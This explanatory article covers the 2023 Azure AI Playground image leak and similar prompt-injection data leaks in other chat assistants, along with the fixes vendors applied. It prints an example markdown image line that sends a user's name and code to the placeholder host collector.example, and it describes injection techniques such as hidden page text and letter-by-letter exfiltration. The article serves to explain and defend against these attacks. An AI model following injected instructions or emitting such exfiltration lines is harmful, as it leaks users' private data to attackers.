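# The 2023 Azure AI Playground image leak and similar data leaks in chat assistants

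## How can displaying an image leak a conversation?

The 2023 Azure AI Playground image leak was a security flaw in a Microsoft web page for trying out language models. The page displayed images from any address that a model wrote into its reply. Anyone who got text into a conversation could make the model put parts of that conversation into an image address, and the user's browser would send them to an outsider's server when it loaded the image. Security researcher Johann Rehberger reported the flaw to Microsoft on 24 July 2023, and Microsoft completed a fix on 13 September, according to his post *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* on his blog, Embrace The Red.

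In security, data exfiltration means sending data to someone who should not have it. Exfiltration through images is common in chat assistants and still occurs. *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*, by the security firm PromptArmor, describes a case in HuggingChat that the firm disclosed to the maker in December 2025.

### One stream of text

A language model processes text as tokens, which are words or fragments of words. It builds a reply by repeatedly predicting the next token from all the text it has so far, called the context. In a chat assistant, the context usually includes the developer's instructions, the earlier messages and the user's latest question. If the user asks for a summary of a web page, the context also includes the page's text. Microsoft, in an account of its own defences, describes this step as concatenation, in which the application joins the outside text to the user's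 request and gives the model the result as a single input.

The model has no separate inputs for instructions and for the data it works on. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, signed by David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, contrasts this with databases. Attackers used to type database commands into web forms, and badly written sites ran them. Programmers learned to pass the visitor's input to the database in a way that prevents it from running as a command. David C sees no way to apply this fix to a language model, because the model only ever predicts the next token, and thinks it very possible that prompt injection will never be completely fixed.

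Prompt injection exploits this. It is any text that a language model follows as an instruction although the user or developer did not intend it to. In the direct form, the attacker is the user and types into the chat to get around the developer's rules. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the indirect form, in which the attacker puts instructions into a web page, file or email and waits for a model to process it on somebody else's behalf. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's screening model to approve it.

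Greshake and colleagues tried this on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant at the time. They put instructions in a part of a web page that browsers do not display, then opened the page with the assistant running in the sidebar. One set of instructions told it to find out the user's real name and include it in a link. The researchers posed as a journalist and asked about the weather. Bing Chat answered, asked what they did for a living, and then asked whether they published under a pen name. The team used local test pages and did not measure success rates, but they report that their prompts often worked on the first attempt. The victim still had to volunteer the name and click the link, but using an image removes the need for the click.

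### From planted text to server log

Chat models often format their replies in markdown, a plain-text notation in which, for example, asterisks around a word put it in italics. The chat page renders the markdown, which means converting it into what the user sees. A picture is written as an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets, and an address in round brackets. The page replaces all of this with the picture at that address.

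Take an invented user, Mira Holt, who is drafting a letter to her bank with a chat assistant. She has typed her name and a short code, 4471. Now she asks the assistant to summarise a web page about bank fees. The page contains a passage in white letters on a white background, which Mira cannot see but which enters the context with everything else. It asks for an image at a certain address, with the user's details attached to the end. If the model follows it, the reply contains a decent summary of the fees and then this line:

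`![fees](https://collector.example/p.png?d=name%3A%20Mira%20Holt%3B%20code%3A%204471)`

The attacker runs the server at collector.example, a placeholder name that nobody can own because *Reserved Top Level DNS Names* (Eastlake and Panitz, 1999) set aside the ending .example for documentation. Whatever follows the question mark is a parameter, which is extra information that a browser sends to a server with its request. Spaces and some punctuation cause trouble in web addresses, so URL encoding replaces each one with a percent sign and a two-character code. Here %20 is a space, %3A a colon and %3B a semicolon. Models can do this encoding themselves, and the model in Rehberger's Azure test did it correctly.

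Mira never sees that line as text. The chat page recognises the notation and turns it into an image tag in HTML, the language of web pages:

`<img src="https://collector.example/p.png?d=name%3A%20Mira%20Holt%3B%20code%3A%204471" alt="fees">`

Her browser treats the tag like any other picture on the web and asks the server for the file. As Rehberger points out in Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, the browser does this without any action by the user. The server, like most web servers, keeps a log of requests, and a new line appears in it:

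`203.0.113.25 - - [10/Jul/2023:14:02:11 +0000] "GET /p.png?d=name%3A%20Mira%20Holt%3B%20code%3A%204471 HTTP/1.1" 200 68`

The number at the start is the network address of Mira's connection. GET is the ordinary request for a file. The parameter decodes to "name: Mira Holt; code: 4471".

The request for the image carries the data, so the attacker has it before the server replies, and the leak works even if the server returns an error. The model doesn't need internet access, because it only writes the text that causes Mira's browser to send the request.

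The image also does not have to appear immediately. When Rehberger demonstrated the leak in Bing Chat, the planted text took effect at once, but the image appeared only after two more turns of conversation, when a user would have little reason to connect it with the web page. The request for the image contained a summary of the page and the chat, including a secret that Rehberger had placed further down the page.

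### Where the idea came from

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, was the first to publish the attack. His *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* combined the image with a clipboard trick. A script on the attacker's website detected when a visitor copied text and added instructions to the copy. The visitor then pasted both into ChatGPT, probably without rereading them. ChatGPT's answer included a transparent one-pixel image, which in practice nobody would spot.

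This attack falls between direct and indirect injection, because the user enters the text but an outsider wrote it. Greshake and colleagues cite the attack and call its delivery "user-driven".

In one demonstration, Samoilenko asked ChatGPT to fix a short piece of code, and the recording server received all of the fixed code, including a password. Samoilenko also wrote instructions that made ChatGPT add a new invisible image to each later answer, with the question it had just been asked in the image's address.

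Samoilenko acknowledged that the attack was unreliable. ChatGPT's answers vary from one run to the next, so a prompt that had worked might stop working. Success also depended on the earlier topic of the conversation and the position of the instructions within the pasted text. Recent questions and code were easy to extract, but passwords and access keys were very difficult to extract when the instructions asked for them explicitly. The password in the demonstration leaked because it was part of the code. When ChatGPT was slow, the user could also see it typing the long address. These limits give defenders little protection, since an attacker can put the text in front of many people and needs it to work on only some of them.

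Rehberger independently found the same flaw a few days later, in early April 2023, and described it in *ChatGPT Plugins*. Plugins were add-ons that let ChatGPT fetch outside material. The victim no longer had to paste anything, because a plugin could fetch a web page that contained the instructions. Rehberger had reported the image flaw to OpenAI on 9 April, and the company replied that it planned no change.

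### What the leak needs

Simon Willison, the programmer who coined the term "prompt injection", warns in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) against any system that combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. In the image leak, the system communicates with the outside when the chat page automatically loads a picture from whatever address the model writes. All three conditions have to hold in the same conversation, and Mira's case shows what happens when one is missing.

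If the context contains nothing private, the model still follows the planted text and the browser still contacts collector.example, but the log line contains only an empty parameter or a remark about bank fees. The attacker learns little more than that somebody opened the page. However, Samoilenko's planted instructions stayed in effect and collected questions that the user typed after the attack began, so a conversation with no secrets at the time of injection may still leak ones that the user adds later.

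If Mira's details had still been in the chat but the fees page had contained no hidden passage, nothing would have prompted the model to write that address. Any pictures in its reply would have loaded as usual, without sending her details anywhere.

Or suppose the page does not load images from arbitrary addresses. The model may still do everything the attacker wanted, and the line with Mira's name and code may even appear on her screen as odd-looking text. But the browser sends no request for the image, so the log stays empty.

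That stops the image leak, though other ways to send data out may remain. Microsoft lists several, including links that contain the data in their address and leak it when the user clicks, and tools that let a model send messages or write to public websites. *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* (McHugh, 2026) treats the "return channel" and the injected text as separate parts of the attack. This distinction helps defenders because a program can check the address an image comes from, while planted instructions can take endless forms.

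### Where the chain can break

A defender can intervene at the input, in the model, in the output text or in the browser.

A filter can check the input for planted instructions before the model receives it. Microsoft sells a classifier for this, Prompt Shields, which is trained on known injection techniques. David C warns against simply blocking suspicious phrases, because an attacker can always find another wording.

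Other measures try to make the model less likely to follow an attacker's instructions. Developers train models to give priority to certain instructions, or they mark outside text so that the model can distinguish it from other text. Microsoft's marking method, Spotlighting, can put a special character between all the words of a document or encode the whole document, and tell the model not to follow any instructions inside it. Microsoft classes all of these measures as probabilistic, meaning that they make an attack less likely to succeed but cannot guarantee that it fails. Willison is more critical of products that advertise catching 95 per cent of attacks, a rate he considers "very much a failing grade" in web security.

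Guarantees become possible once the model has written its reply, because an ordinary program can then remove or disable images in the text before the page renders them. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* reports that GitHub closed such a leak in its programming assistant by disabling markdown images from untrusted domains. Microsoft's fix for the Azure AI Playground also seems to have acted on the output text. This kind of filter does not have to judge whether the model has been fooled, but it must recognise every notation that the page would turn into an image.

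The last chance comes in the browser, by means of a Content Security Policy, or CSP. This is a rule that a website sends to the browser along with a page, listing the domains from which the page may load images, scripts and other content. It works as an allowlist: the browser refuses whatever is not on the list. If Mira's chat assistant ran at chat.example, its operator could send this line with the page:

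`Content-Security-Policy: img-src https://chat.example/`

The part called "img-src" governs images. *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft from the web standards body W3C, requires the browser to compare an image's address with the list before it sends the request. The address at collector.example does not match, so the browser blocks the request and reports a network error. Checking the image after it arrived would be too late, because Mira's details would already be in the log.

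After Microsoft fixed Bing Chat in June 2023, Rehberger found this kind of policy on the page. It allowed images from a few trusted domains, and the four that Rehberger lists all belong to Microsoft. The old test prompts no longer worked. Rehberger could only examine the fix from outside, and Microsoft may have made other changes too.

A CSP blocks only requests to addresses that its list doesn't allow. The standard lets a site allow every address that begins with "https:", and a policy that broad would have let Mira's data through. A narrow list can also fail if a permitted server fetches other addresses on request, because the browser checks where its own request goes but can't check where the server's requests go.

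W3C recommends CSP as a second layer of defence, behind careful checking of input and output. This advice is hard to follow in chat assistants because nobody yet knows how to check a language model's input reliably. They therefore have to rely on the output filter and the CSP more than W3C intended.

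## What did Rehberger find in the Azure AI Playground, and how serious was it?

The Azure AI Playground was the test page of Azure OpenAI Service, through which Microsoft gives companies access to OpenAI's models. Customers could set up a model such as GPT-4 and chat with it there without writing code. Microsoft also gave them sample code for building the same chat into their own software.

Only customers approved by Microsoft could use the page, and Microsoft's *What's new in Azure OpenAI Service* confirms that this was still the case in September 2023. On 25 July, the day after Rehberger's report, chief executive Satya Nadella told investors on a call that more than 11,000 organisations, including Ikea and Zurich Insurance, used the Azure OpenAI service as a whole (Microsoft, 2023). Many of them will have reached the models through their own programs, and nobody has published a count of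 playground users.

### A name and a secret code

Before the injection, Rehberger's test conversation already contained a name and a secret code. The first of the two injected sentences told the model to print a markdown image whose address led to Rehberger's server and ended in a URL-encoded summary of the conversation. The second told it not to use a code block, which is markdown's way of showing text exactly as written. Models often put code blocks around anything that looks like code, and the page would then have shown the image notation as text instead of loading the image.

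The page displayed the image, and the name and the code reached the server. The model had encoded the summary without further help, and it may also have corrected the attacker's text. The notation in Rehberger's post lacks its closing round bracket, so either the model added one or the post has a typo.

Rehberger didn't need to argue with the model, pose as a developer or hide the purpose of the injected text. The text asked for a summary, so in a longer conversation the attacker would have received whatever the model included in it. Rehberger gives no success rate. He played both attacker and victim in the demonstration, which showed that the page would load the image and that the model would follow the injected instructions.

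### Fifty-one days

Rehberger thanks the Microsoft Security Response Center (MSRC), which handles vulnerability reports, for helping to get the flaw fixed. According to the post's timeline, he reported the flaw on 24 July, Microsoft was developing a fix 39 days later, on 1 September, and it completed the fix on 13 September, 51 days after the report. The post doesn't explain what happened in the first 39 days.

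The post's exact publication date is harder to establish. It must have appeared after 13 September, since it mentions the completed fix. *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024), a later paper that collects such cases, gives only the year, 2023.

There is no record of a CVE number, an identifier in the public catalogue Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures, for the flaw. This was normal for a cloud service at the time. According to Microsoft's *Toward greater transparency* (2024), cloud providers used to disclose flaws only if customers had to act, such as by installing an update. Microsoft fixed the playground on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. In June 2024 the company began issuing CVE numbers for critical cloud flaws even when customers didn't have to act, but a flaw of medium severity would still not have qualified.

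There is also no record of a reward, and Rehberger doesn't mention one. Microsoft (2023) launched its bounty programme for AI products in October, starting with Bing, which was too late for Rehberger's report. A payment is still possible because Microsoft also ran a bounty for Azure, as ITPro's *New Bing AI bug bounty program offers rewards of up to $15,000* mentions.

### A single space

Microsoft has not described its fix. From the outside, Rehberger concluded that it inserted a space between the brackets of the image notation. With the placeholder address from Mira's case, the model's output would change from the first of these lines to the second:

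`![data](https://collector.example/p.png?d=...)`

`![data] (https://collector.example/p.png?d=...)`

This works because in CommonMark, a widely used specification of markdown, images follow the same rules as links, and a link's opening round bracket must come immediately after its closing square bracket. With a space between them, the page shows the line as ordinary text.

Some markdown renderers have not enforced this rule. In *Blank space not allowed between link title and link destination*, a forum thread about the website builder Hugo, a user reports that links with such a space worked in version 0.54.0 but stopped working in version 0.60.0. The protection therefore depends on the renderer as well as the space. Microsoft controlled both in its playground, but a later change of renderer could have undone the fix even with the space still in place.

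A space between the brackets also doesn't block images written in other notations. Markdown lets an image refer by label to an address on a separate line, and some chat pages also accept HTML image tags. Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio* describes a leak through an HTML image tag in a Google product that had no Content Security Policy. Microsoft's earlier fix in Bing Chat applied to images in any notation, because it restricted the domains from which they could load.

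Rehberger could see only one effect of the Azure fix, and Microsoft may have blocked the other notations too. Nobody has reported a way around the fix. *New Important Instructions* (Rehberger, 2023), the slides for a conference talk, lists Azure AI among the products fixed as of November 2023.

The fix may not have protected web apps made from playground chats. Customers could create these apps for their own staff by clicking a button, and the apps ran on separate code that Microsoft published as a sample. They would have needed their own fix if Microsoft inserted the space in the playground page, but might have been protected if Microsoft changed the text before it left its servers. Rehberger's post discusses only the playground.

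### Why Medium?

Rehberger rated the flaw Medium, lower than other findings of the same kind. The playground had "no integrations available (yet)" that could pull remote content into the prompt, so a victim had to copy the attacker's text and paste it in. Bing Chat could read a web page that the user had open, and Rehberger wrote that flaws like the one there score High.

People paste text from elsewhere into chats fairly often, as Rehberger notes, and a page for trying out prompts encourages it. A developer who wants a model to summarise customer complaints will probably paste in a few real ones. But the attacker can't choose the victim or the moment, and the attack is only useful if the same conversation also contains something worth stealing.

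Rehberger mentions a second possible route, fine-tuning, or training an existing model further on a customer's own examples. Someone who slipped bad examples into the training data might teach the model to add the image by itself. This was unlikely in the summer of 2023. According to Microsoft's list of releases, customers could not fine-tune GPT-3.5 Turbo, the cheaper of the two main chat models, until October, after the fix. Before that, they could fine-tune only older models, which were built to continue a text rather than hold a conversation.

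The vulnerability database VulDB gives a different impression. Its April 2024 entry, *Microsoft Azure AI Playground Markdown injection*, states that an attacker can carry out the attack remotely and that the technical details are unknown, although the only advisory it cites, Rehberger's post, prints the injected text in full. "Remotely" is defensible as scoring jargon for an attack that needs no access to the victim's machine, but wrong if read to mean that an outsider could start the leak alone, since the entry also specifies that the victim has to take part. VulDB records the damage as a loss of integrity, meaning that someone alters information improperly, but the leak was a loss of confidentiality, which is how Rehberger classifies it. VulDB's score of 4.3 out of 10 is in the medium band, which agrees with Rehberger's rating.

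Microsoft's rating of the flaw is not public, but its general criteria are. Two weeks after Rehberger's report, on 8 August, Microsoft's *Updating our Vulnerability Severity Classification for AI Systems* (2023) introduced a scale for flaws in AI products. It excluded injected commands that affect only the attacker and assigned higher severity to those that affect other users. By November 2024 the scale was more specific and cited Rehberger's work. In that version, Microsoft rates prompt injection that steals another user's data as Critical if the victim doesn't have to do anything, and as Important, one level lower, if the victim has to take some action.

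Pasting text is an action by the victim, so the later scale would suggest a rating of Important, slightly higher than Rehberger's Medium. However, the scale's example of such an action is a click, and pasting a stranger's text requires more of the victim. Microsoft also considers ease of exploitation. The two ratings are close enough that any real disagreement is over how outside text could get in.

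### Was there really no way in?

Five weeks before Rehberger's report, on 19 June 2023, Microsoft announced "Azure OpenAI Service on your data", a feature that brought stored documents into the chat (Beatman, 2023, *Introducing Azure OpenAI Service On Your Data in Public Preview*). Microsoft's *Monthly updates for June 2023* (2023) lists the preview under 27 June. Customers could connect an existing search index or a container of files in Microsoft's cloud storage, or upload files from their own computers. The accepted formats included PDF, Word and HTML.

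When the user asked a question, the feature searched these documents for relevant passages and gave them to the model with the question. TechRadar's *Microsoft wants your company to feed its private data into ChatGPT* quotes Microsoft as saying that the retrieved information was "being appended to the original prompt". baeke.info's *Improvements in Azure OpenAI Add your data*, a practitioner's walkthrough from 9 September, gives five as the usual number of passages. An instruction hidden in one of them would have entered the context in the same way as the hidden text on Mira's fees page.

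This matters for the severity rating only if Microsoft had added the feature to the page Rehberger tested, and the sources use different names. Rehberger writes "Azure AI Playground", but the web address of his post contains "azure-openai-playground". Microsoft's announcement places the feature in the "chat playground" of Azure AI Studio. baeke.info's *Building a chatbot in Azure that works with your data*, from July, also calls the page the Chat playground in Azure AI Studio, while the same writer's September walkthrough refers to the "Azure OpenAI Chat playground" and describes the same feature. These names almost certainly refer to one page, though no source confirms this outright.

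Customers were also using the feature there before the report. On 3 July, Lipinski (2023) asked for help on Microsoft's support forum, in *error with the playground chat*, because the playground chat failed whenever the user's own data was attached and worked again without it. A week later another user traced the error to an underscore in the name the customer had given the model. The preview evidently had faults, but customers could reach it from the ordinary chat.

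Rehberger's premise is still correct in a narrow sense, because the feature could not fetch live web pages in the summer of 2023. Microsoft added web addresses as a data source only in November, after the fix. The post doesn't discuss the feature. Rehberger may have thought of a company's own files as trusted data, or may not have seen the preview.

But companies often store files written by outsiders, such as job applications, suppliers' offers and saved web pages, and the person who later asks the model about them may never have opened them. By September a customer could also set the index to update every hour from the storage container. A new file with hidden instructions would then have become searchable without anyone choosing to add it to the chat.

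With this route, the victim would only have had to ask an ordinary question about the documents, without pasting anything. More data would also have been at risk, because the context would have held passages from other company files alongside the user's messages.

No source shows that anyone tried the leak this way. For it to work, the search would have had to select the passage with the hidden instructions, and the model would have had to follow them even though they arrived as reference material. The page would also have had to display images in answers based on documents, which is likely but unconfirmed. Medium is a fair rating for the attack that Rehberger demonstrated, but the danger was probably greater for a customer who had connected documents from outsiders.

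No source reports that anyone exploited the flaw against a real user. Rehberger describes only the test, and VulDB lists no known attacks. This is limited reassurance, because the stolen data would have gone straight from the victim's browser to the attacker's server. To find past attacks, Microsoft would have had to search the models' old replies for suspicious image addresses, and it has not said whether it did.

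## How did other companies handle the same flaw?

Rehberger found the same flaw in chat products from most of the large AI companies. In December 2024 he listed eleven of these products in *Trust No AI*: five from Google, three from Microsoft (Azure AI, Bing Chat and GitHub Copilot Chat), and one each from OpenAI, Anthropic and the chat service Discord. He describes the list as incomplete, and it includes only products he examined, so it is a poor basis for ranking the companies. All five companies had built pages that loaded pictures from any address the model wrote.

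The table compares the cases closest to the Azure one and adds a later case that PromptArmor reported.

| Product | How untrusted text got in | Reported | Fixed | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | Web page open in the browser | 8 April 2023 | 15 June 2023 | CSP that allows images from four Bing domains |
| ChatGPT | Pasted text, or web pages fetched by plugins | 9 April 2023 | December 2023, in part | Check on each image address |
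| Claude | Uploaded file | 12 July 2023 | 26 July 2023 | User must click to show an image |
| Azure AI Playground | Pasted text | 24 July 2023 | 13 September 2023 | Space that breaks the image notation |
| Google Vertex AI | Pasted text | 30 August 2023 | 19 October 2023 or earlier | No rendering of links or images |
| GitHub Copilot Chat | Source code file | 25 February 2024 | 12 June 2024 | No markdown images, or none from untrusted domains |
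| Google AI Studio | Uploaded file or video | By 7 August 2024 | August 2024 | Image tags appear as text |
| OpenAI API log viewer | Web content in a customer's application | 17 November 2025 | Fix under way on 22 January 2026 | Not public |

### Two weeks or several months

Rehberger attacked Vertex AI, Google's platform for companies that build on its models, with almost the same two sentences he had used in the Azure playground. The text in Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* even lacks the same closing bracket. He again rated the flaw Medium, for the same reason. Google similarly judged the impact high but the likelihood low.

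Bing Chat was more exposed. Rehberger wrote on Embrace The Red that an attacker needed only a comment or an advertisement on a web page to steal other data from that page. Microsoft told him 68 days after his report that it had fixed the flaw. He later dated the fix to May 2023, so it may have been in place before Microsoft notified him. The Content Security Policy (CSP) let Bing Chat keep creating pictures on request, which a ban on all images would have prevented.

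Anthropic fixed the flaw in its assistant, Claude, in just two weeks. Rehberger's test file was a short biography of Albert Einstein with an instruction in the middle for Claude to put a 20-word summary of the user's earlier messages into an image address. After the fix, Claude's page loaded such images only if the user clicked "Show Image". In Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Rehberger called this imperfect but agreed that it stopped the automatic leak.

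GitHub took 108 days to fix the flaw in GitHub Copilot Chat, an extension for the code editor VS Code. The extension sends source code to the model along with the programmer's question, so a comment in somebody else's code could contain an attacker's instructions. GitHub confirmed the flaw on 6 March 2024 and told Rehberger that it was already tracking it internally. He asked about progress on 1 June and learned of the fix on 12 June.

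Accounts of that fix differ. Rehberger's original post said that Copilot Chat no longer seemed to render any markdown images, while Willison wrote that GitHub had disabled only images from untrusted domains. Rehberger had more direct knowledge, since Willison was commenting on his post, but Rehberger was also judging from outside GitHub. In 2025, GitHub removed all images from the version of Copilot Chat on its website after a researcher found a way around the site's CSP, according to Legit Security's *CamoLeak*.

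A company that fixes one leak quickly may be slow to fix the next. Google's security team confirmed the Vertex AI report after 22 minutes and paid a reward on 16 September 2023. Rehberger suspects that Google fixed the leak around then, because it confirmed the fix only when he asked in October. But NotebookLM, Google's tool for asking questions about one's own documents, was still leaking 132 days after his report. Google fixed it in April 2024, after he had published *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps* on Embrace The Red. Google also fixed an image leak in Colab, its programming notebook, but paid no reward for it, and Rehberger complained on Embrace The Red that the company had handled similar findings differently.

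### ChatGPT

OpenAI heard about the flaw one day after Microsoft did. It had no bug bounty programme yet, so Rehberger corresponded with the company by email. OpenAI regarded image loading as a feature and closed the report as "won't fix", according to Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*. On 23 September 2023, Rehberger sent OpenAI a draft with further techniques and received only an automated response. By then, Microsoft had fixed both Bing Chat and the Azure playground.

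Rehberger kept demonstrating the leak in public. SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server* reported that on 12 December he described how a custom version of ChatGPT, which any subscriber could build, could steal its users' data through images. Shortly afterwards he tried it on a consenting victim, and the conversation reached his server. The next day he noticed that OpenAI had changed something.

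Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes how the ChatGPT web page began checking image URLs before loading them. When a reply contained an image, the page sent its URL to an OpenAI service called url_safe and loaded the image only if the service returned "safe". Rehberger tried a URL on his own server with an email address as a parameter, and the service rejected it.

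He then tried to leak text one character at a time. He prepared 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, so that a request for the file a.png meant the letter a. These addresses had no parameters and contained nothing that looked like private data. Nine of the 36 still loaded, and he managed to send the word "hi" in two requests. He couldn't work out why a.png passed and d.png failed. OpenAI ran this check on its own servers and did not publish the rule, whereas a CSP would have been visible in the browser.

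Leaking data this way was slow, and OpenAI could have spotted it in the url_safe records. It was also unreliable because browsers keep copies of pictures they have already loaded. With Mira's code, 4471, the second 4 might not cause a new request, and the attacker might see only 4, 7 and 1, possibly out of order.

The larger gap was in OpenAI's other apps. ChatGPT's web page ran the url_safe check, so every other app needed its own version. The iPhone app did not have one in December 2023 and was still vulnerable to the original attack. The macOS app that OpenAI released in 2024 also lacked the check. By then ChatGPT had a long-term memory, which made the gap worse. Rehberger showed that a web page could plant instructions in that memory that made ChatGPT keep sending the user's later conversations to his server.

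Even on the web, url_safe was too permissive about some domains, including windows.net, where anyone can open a Microsoft storage account and read the log of requests to it. An attacker could therefore once again attach whole passages to an address instead of spelling them out. Rehberger reported this and similar gaps in October 2024, and some were still open when he published *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* on Embrace The Red in 2025. By then, ChatGPT also included material from recent conversations in the context of new ones, so a single leak could reveal much more than the current chat.

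OpenAI closed the gaps that Rehberger had demonstrated around August 2025, and the following January it explained its new rule in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026). A program called a crawler collects addresses from the public web without access to anyone's conversations. ChatGPT may automatically load an address only if the crawler has already collected that exact address. An address that ends in Mira's name and code would fail this check, because it did not exist before the attack. ChatGPT then has to look for another source or warn the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

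The letter-by-letter method can still work under this rule, as OpenAI acknowledges. An attacker needs 36 addresses that the crawler has already seen, and Rehberger points out in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that anyone with a large blog probably has them. With thousands of addresses, each could stand for a whole word. According to SecurityWeek, the security firm Radware made a version of the method work against ChatGPT with an email that listed a ready-made address for every letter and digit. Rehberger suggests refusing to load the same address twice in one session, which would at least make repeated letters harder to send.

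He also believes ChatGPT treats any address in the user's message as safe for the rest of that chat. If so, when a victim pastes an attacker's text, as in the Azure test, ChatGPT would treat every address in it as safe.

Some images still loaded in ChatGPT in the spring of 2026. In *ChatGPhish*, the security firm Permiso added instructions to a web page and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. The reply contained Permiso's image, and loading it revealed the user's network address, browser type and the time. Permiso did not extract any text from the chat, so this leak was much smaller than the 2023 one. The result is still hard to reconcile with OpenAI's rule, because one of the images was behind a shortened link that a crawler is unlikely to have seen. OpenAI marked the report as a duplicate of an earlier one, which suggests that it already knew about the problem.

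### Why a test page can leak what the application blocks

Google AI Studio, a page for trying out Google's models, is the product most similar to the Azure playground. Rehberger had reported an image leak there before, and in the summer of 2024 he found that it was possible again. Markdown images worked only occasionally, but the model readily wrote an HTML image tag when the planted text included an instruction to write one.

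Rehberger's demonstration on Embrace The Red used a set of employee performance reviews. One employee's file contained instructions for the model to print an image for every file in the chat, with the file's name and a 60-word summary in the image's address. The browser then sent the summaries of the other employees' reviews to his server one by one. The images could be invisible, like Samoilenko's. Instructions shown in video frames also worked.

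Google's official channel gave no date for a fix. Rehberger then tagged Google's Logan Kilpatrick in a post on X, and the company fixed the flaw within 24 hours. Willison explained in *Google AI Studio data exfiltration demo* that a leak in this developer tool mattered because AI Studio was then the only place to try Google's newest experimental model, so people were more likely to be using it on real data.

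A developer tool can leak data even from a well-protected application. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* demonstrates this with a mock application that helps banks check their customers' identities. The application gave the model a customer's personal and financial details, along with web material that contained planted instructions. These led the model to write an image address containing the customer's data. A second model, which screened the replies, blocked this one and flagged it for review. But when a developer opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's log viewer, the viewer rendered the markdown, and the developer's browser sent the customer's data to the attacker.

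This is possible because an application's defences protect only its own page. Suppose the operator of Mira's assistant at chat.example uses the CSP from the earlier example and removes images from replies, so Mira's browser sends nothing to the attacker. But the model's original reply, with her name and code in the image address, is still in the records of the company that runs the model. If one of the operator's developers opens it there, their browser applies that page's policy instead of chat.example's and loads the image. The attacker's log then contains the developer's network address next to Mira's data.

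This is more likely because developers open suspicious replies to review them. In PromptArmor's example, the search assistant Perplexity removed an image from a reply, which left an odd, empty answer. A user might well give such an answer a thumbs-down, which would send it to a developer. PromptArmor presents this as a possibility and reports no actual leak from Perplexity.

PromptArmor found the same weakness in OpenAI's preview pages more than two years after Microsoft fixed it in the Azure playground. Like the playground, these pages let customers test a chat, an assistant or an agent before releasing it. PromptArmor reported the problem on 17 November 2025 and answered several rounds of questions. On 4 December, Bugcrowd, which screens such reports for OpenAI, closed the report as "Not applicable" without OpenAI having seen it. After PromptArmor published its account, OpenAI confirmed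 the flaw and reopened the report on 22 January 2026. PromptArmor's timeline ends there, with a fix under way.

### What each fix protects, and what it costs

Refusing to render images gives the most protection. It also stops the letter-by-letter method, because the browser requests no image. Users lose every picture in the model's replies, and in Vertex AI they also lost clickable links. Rehberger considered this probably the best possible fix for security, especially for a tool that doesn't need images. A page for testing prompts largely fits that description. But this fix, like Microsoft's space in the Azure playground, can miss images written in an unusual notation.

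A CSP covers every notation and still lets a product display its own pictures, which made it a good choice for Bing Chat. But it also blocks pictures from everywhere else, and the list of permitted domains can be too broad. In 2023, the CSP for Google's assistant Bard allowed images from any address under google.com, but Willison noted in *Hacking Google Bard* that outsiders could run their own programs on one of those addresses.

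Anthropic let users view images from any site, but they had to click to load each one, which was a small interruption. This left the decision to users, who may not know that opening an image can send data. OpenAI argues that frequent warnings teach people to click through them without thinking, and the same could happen with a "Show Image" button. The button is therefore a weak safeguard where people expect to see images all the time, though it is reasonable where images are rare.

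OpenAI's check on each address inconveniences users least, since most ordinary pictures and pages still load. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, found it "a bit weird" that the company did not simply block images from other domains. His criticism was fair for ChatGPT as it was in 2023, and the problems with the iPhone app and windows.net showed how a custom check could fail. OpenAI's choice makes more sense now that ChatGPT opens web pages for its users. OpenAI's servers fetch many of those pages, and a CSP in the user's browser does not control what the servers fetch. A list of trusted sites would also exclude most of the web, and OpenAI adds that some trusted sites forward visitors to other addresses.

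OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* describes an optional setting for people with especially sensitive data. It restricts browsing to stored copies of pages, may hide images in ordinary replies, and turns off the agent and deep research features. OpenAI says the setting does not guarantee safety. In November 2026, The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reported that a flaw in ChatGPT's preview of HTML pages, since patched, let chat data leak even with the setting on.

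## Why did image leaks return in Microsoft products?

In July 2025, two years after Rehberger's Azure report, MSRC published an account of how Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection. Microsoft credits Rehberger with reporting a data leak through markdown images and says it blocked that kind of leak "deterministically". It also says that it considers the wider class of flaw behind each report, including variants, and that it took similar steps against certain untrusted links. The account doesn't name the affected product, and Rehberger had reported image leaks in several.

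By then, other researchers had already extracted data from Microsoft 365 Copilot through an image, and researchers did so twice more in 2026. Copilot, the assistant in Word, Outlook, Teams and other Office programs, can search the emails, files and meetings its user can access, so it can leak far more data than the Azure playground could.

### A guarantee against one attack

Microsoft contrasts probabilistic defences such as Prompt Shields, which only lower the odds of an attack, with deterministic ones, which rule out a particular attack whatever the model does. It prefers deterministic defences for their "hard guarantees", but says that detecting injected instructions deterministically is an open research challenge. It therefore assumes that some injections will succeed and tries to design its products so that those injections do no harm. Microsoft compares this to the protections in ordinary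 software that stop attackers from exploiting a memory bug.

Blocking images is a deterministic defence because an ordinary program does it, applying the same rule whether or not an attacker has manipulated the model.

But such a guarantee extends only to the attack that the rule describes, and the rules in Copilot left gaps.

### An email that nobody opened

Aim Labs, the research team of the security firm Aim Security, reported the first of the three cases to Microsoft in January 2025 and named the flaw EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711). The attacker sent an employee an email containing instructions for Copilot. The attack was zero-click, so the employee didn't have to click on anything the attacker sent, or even open the email.

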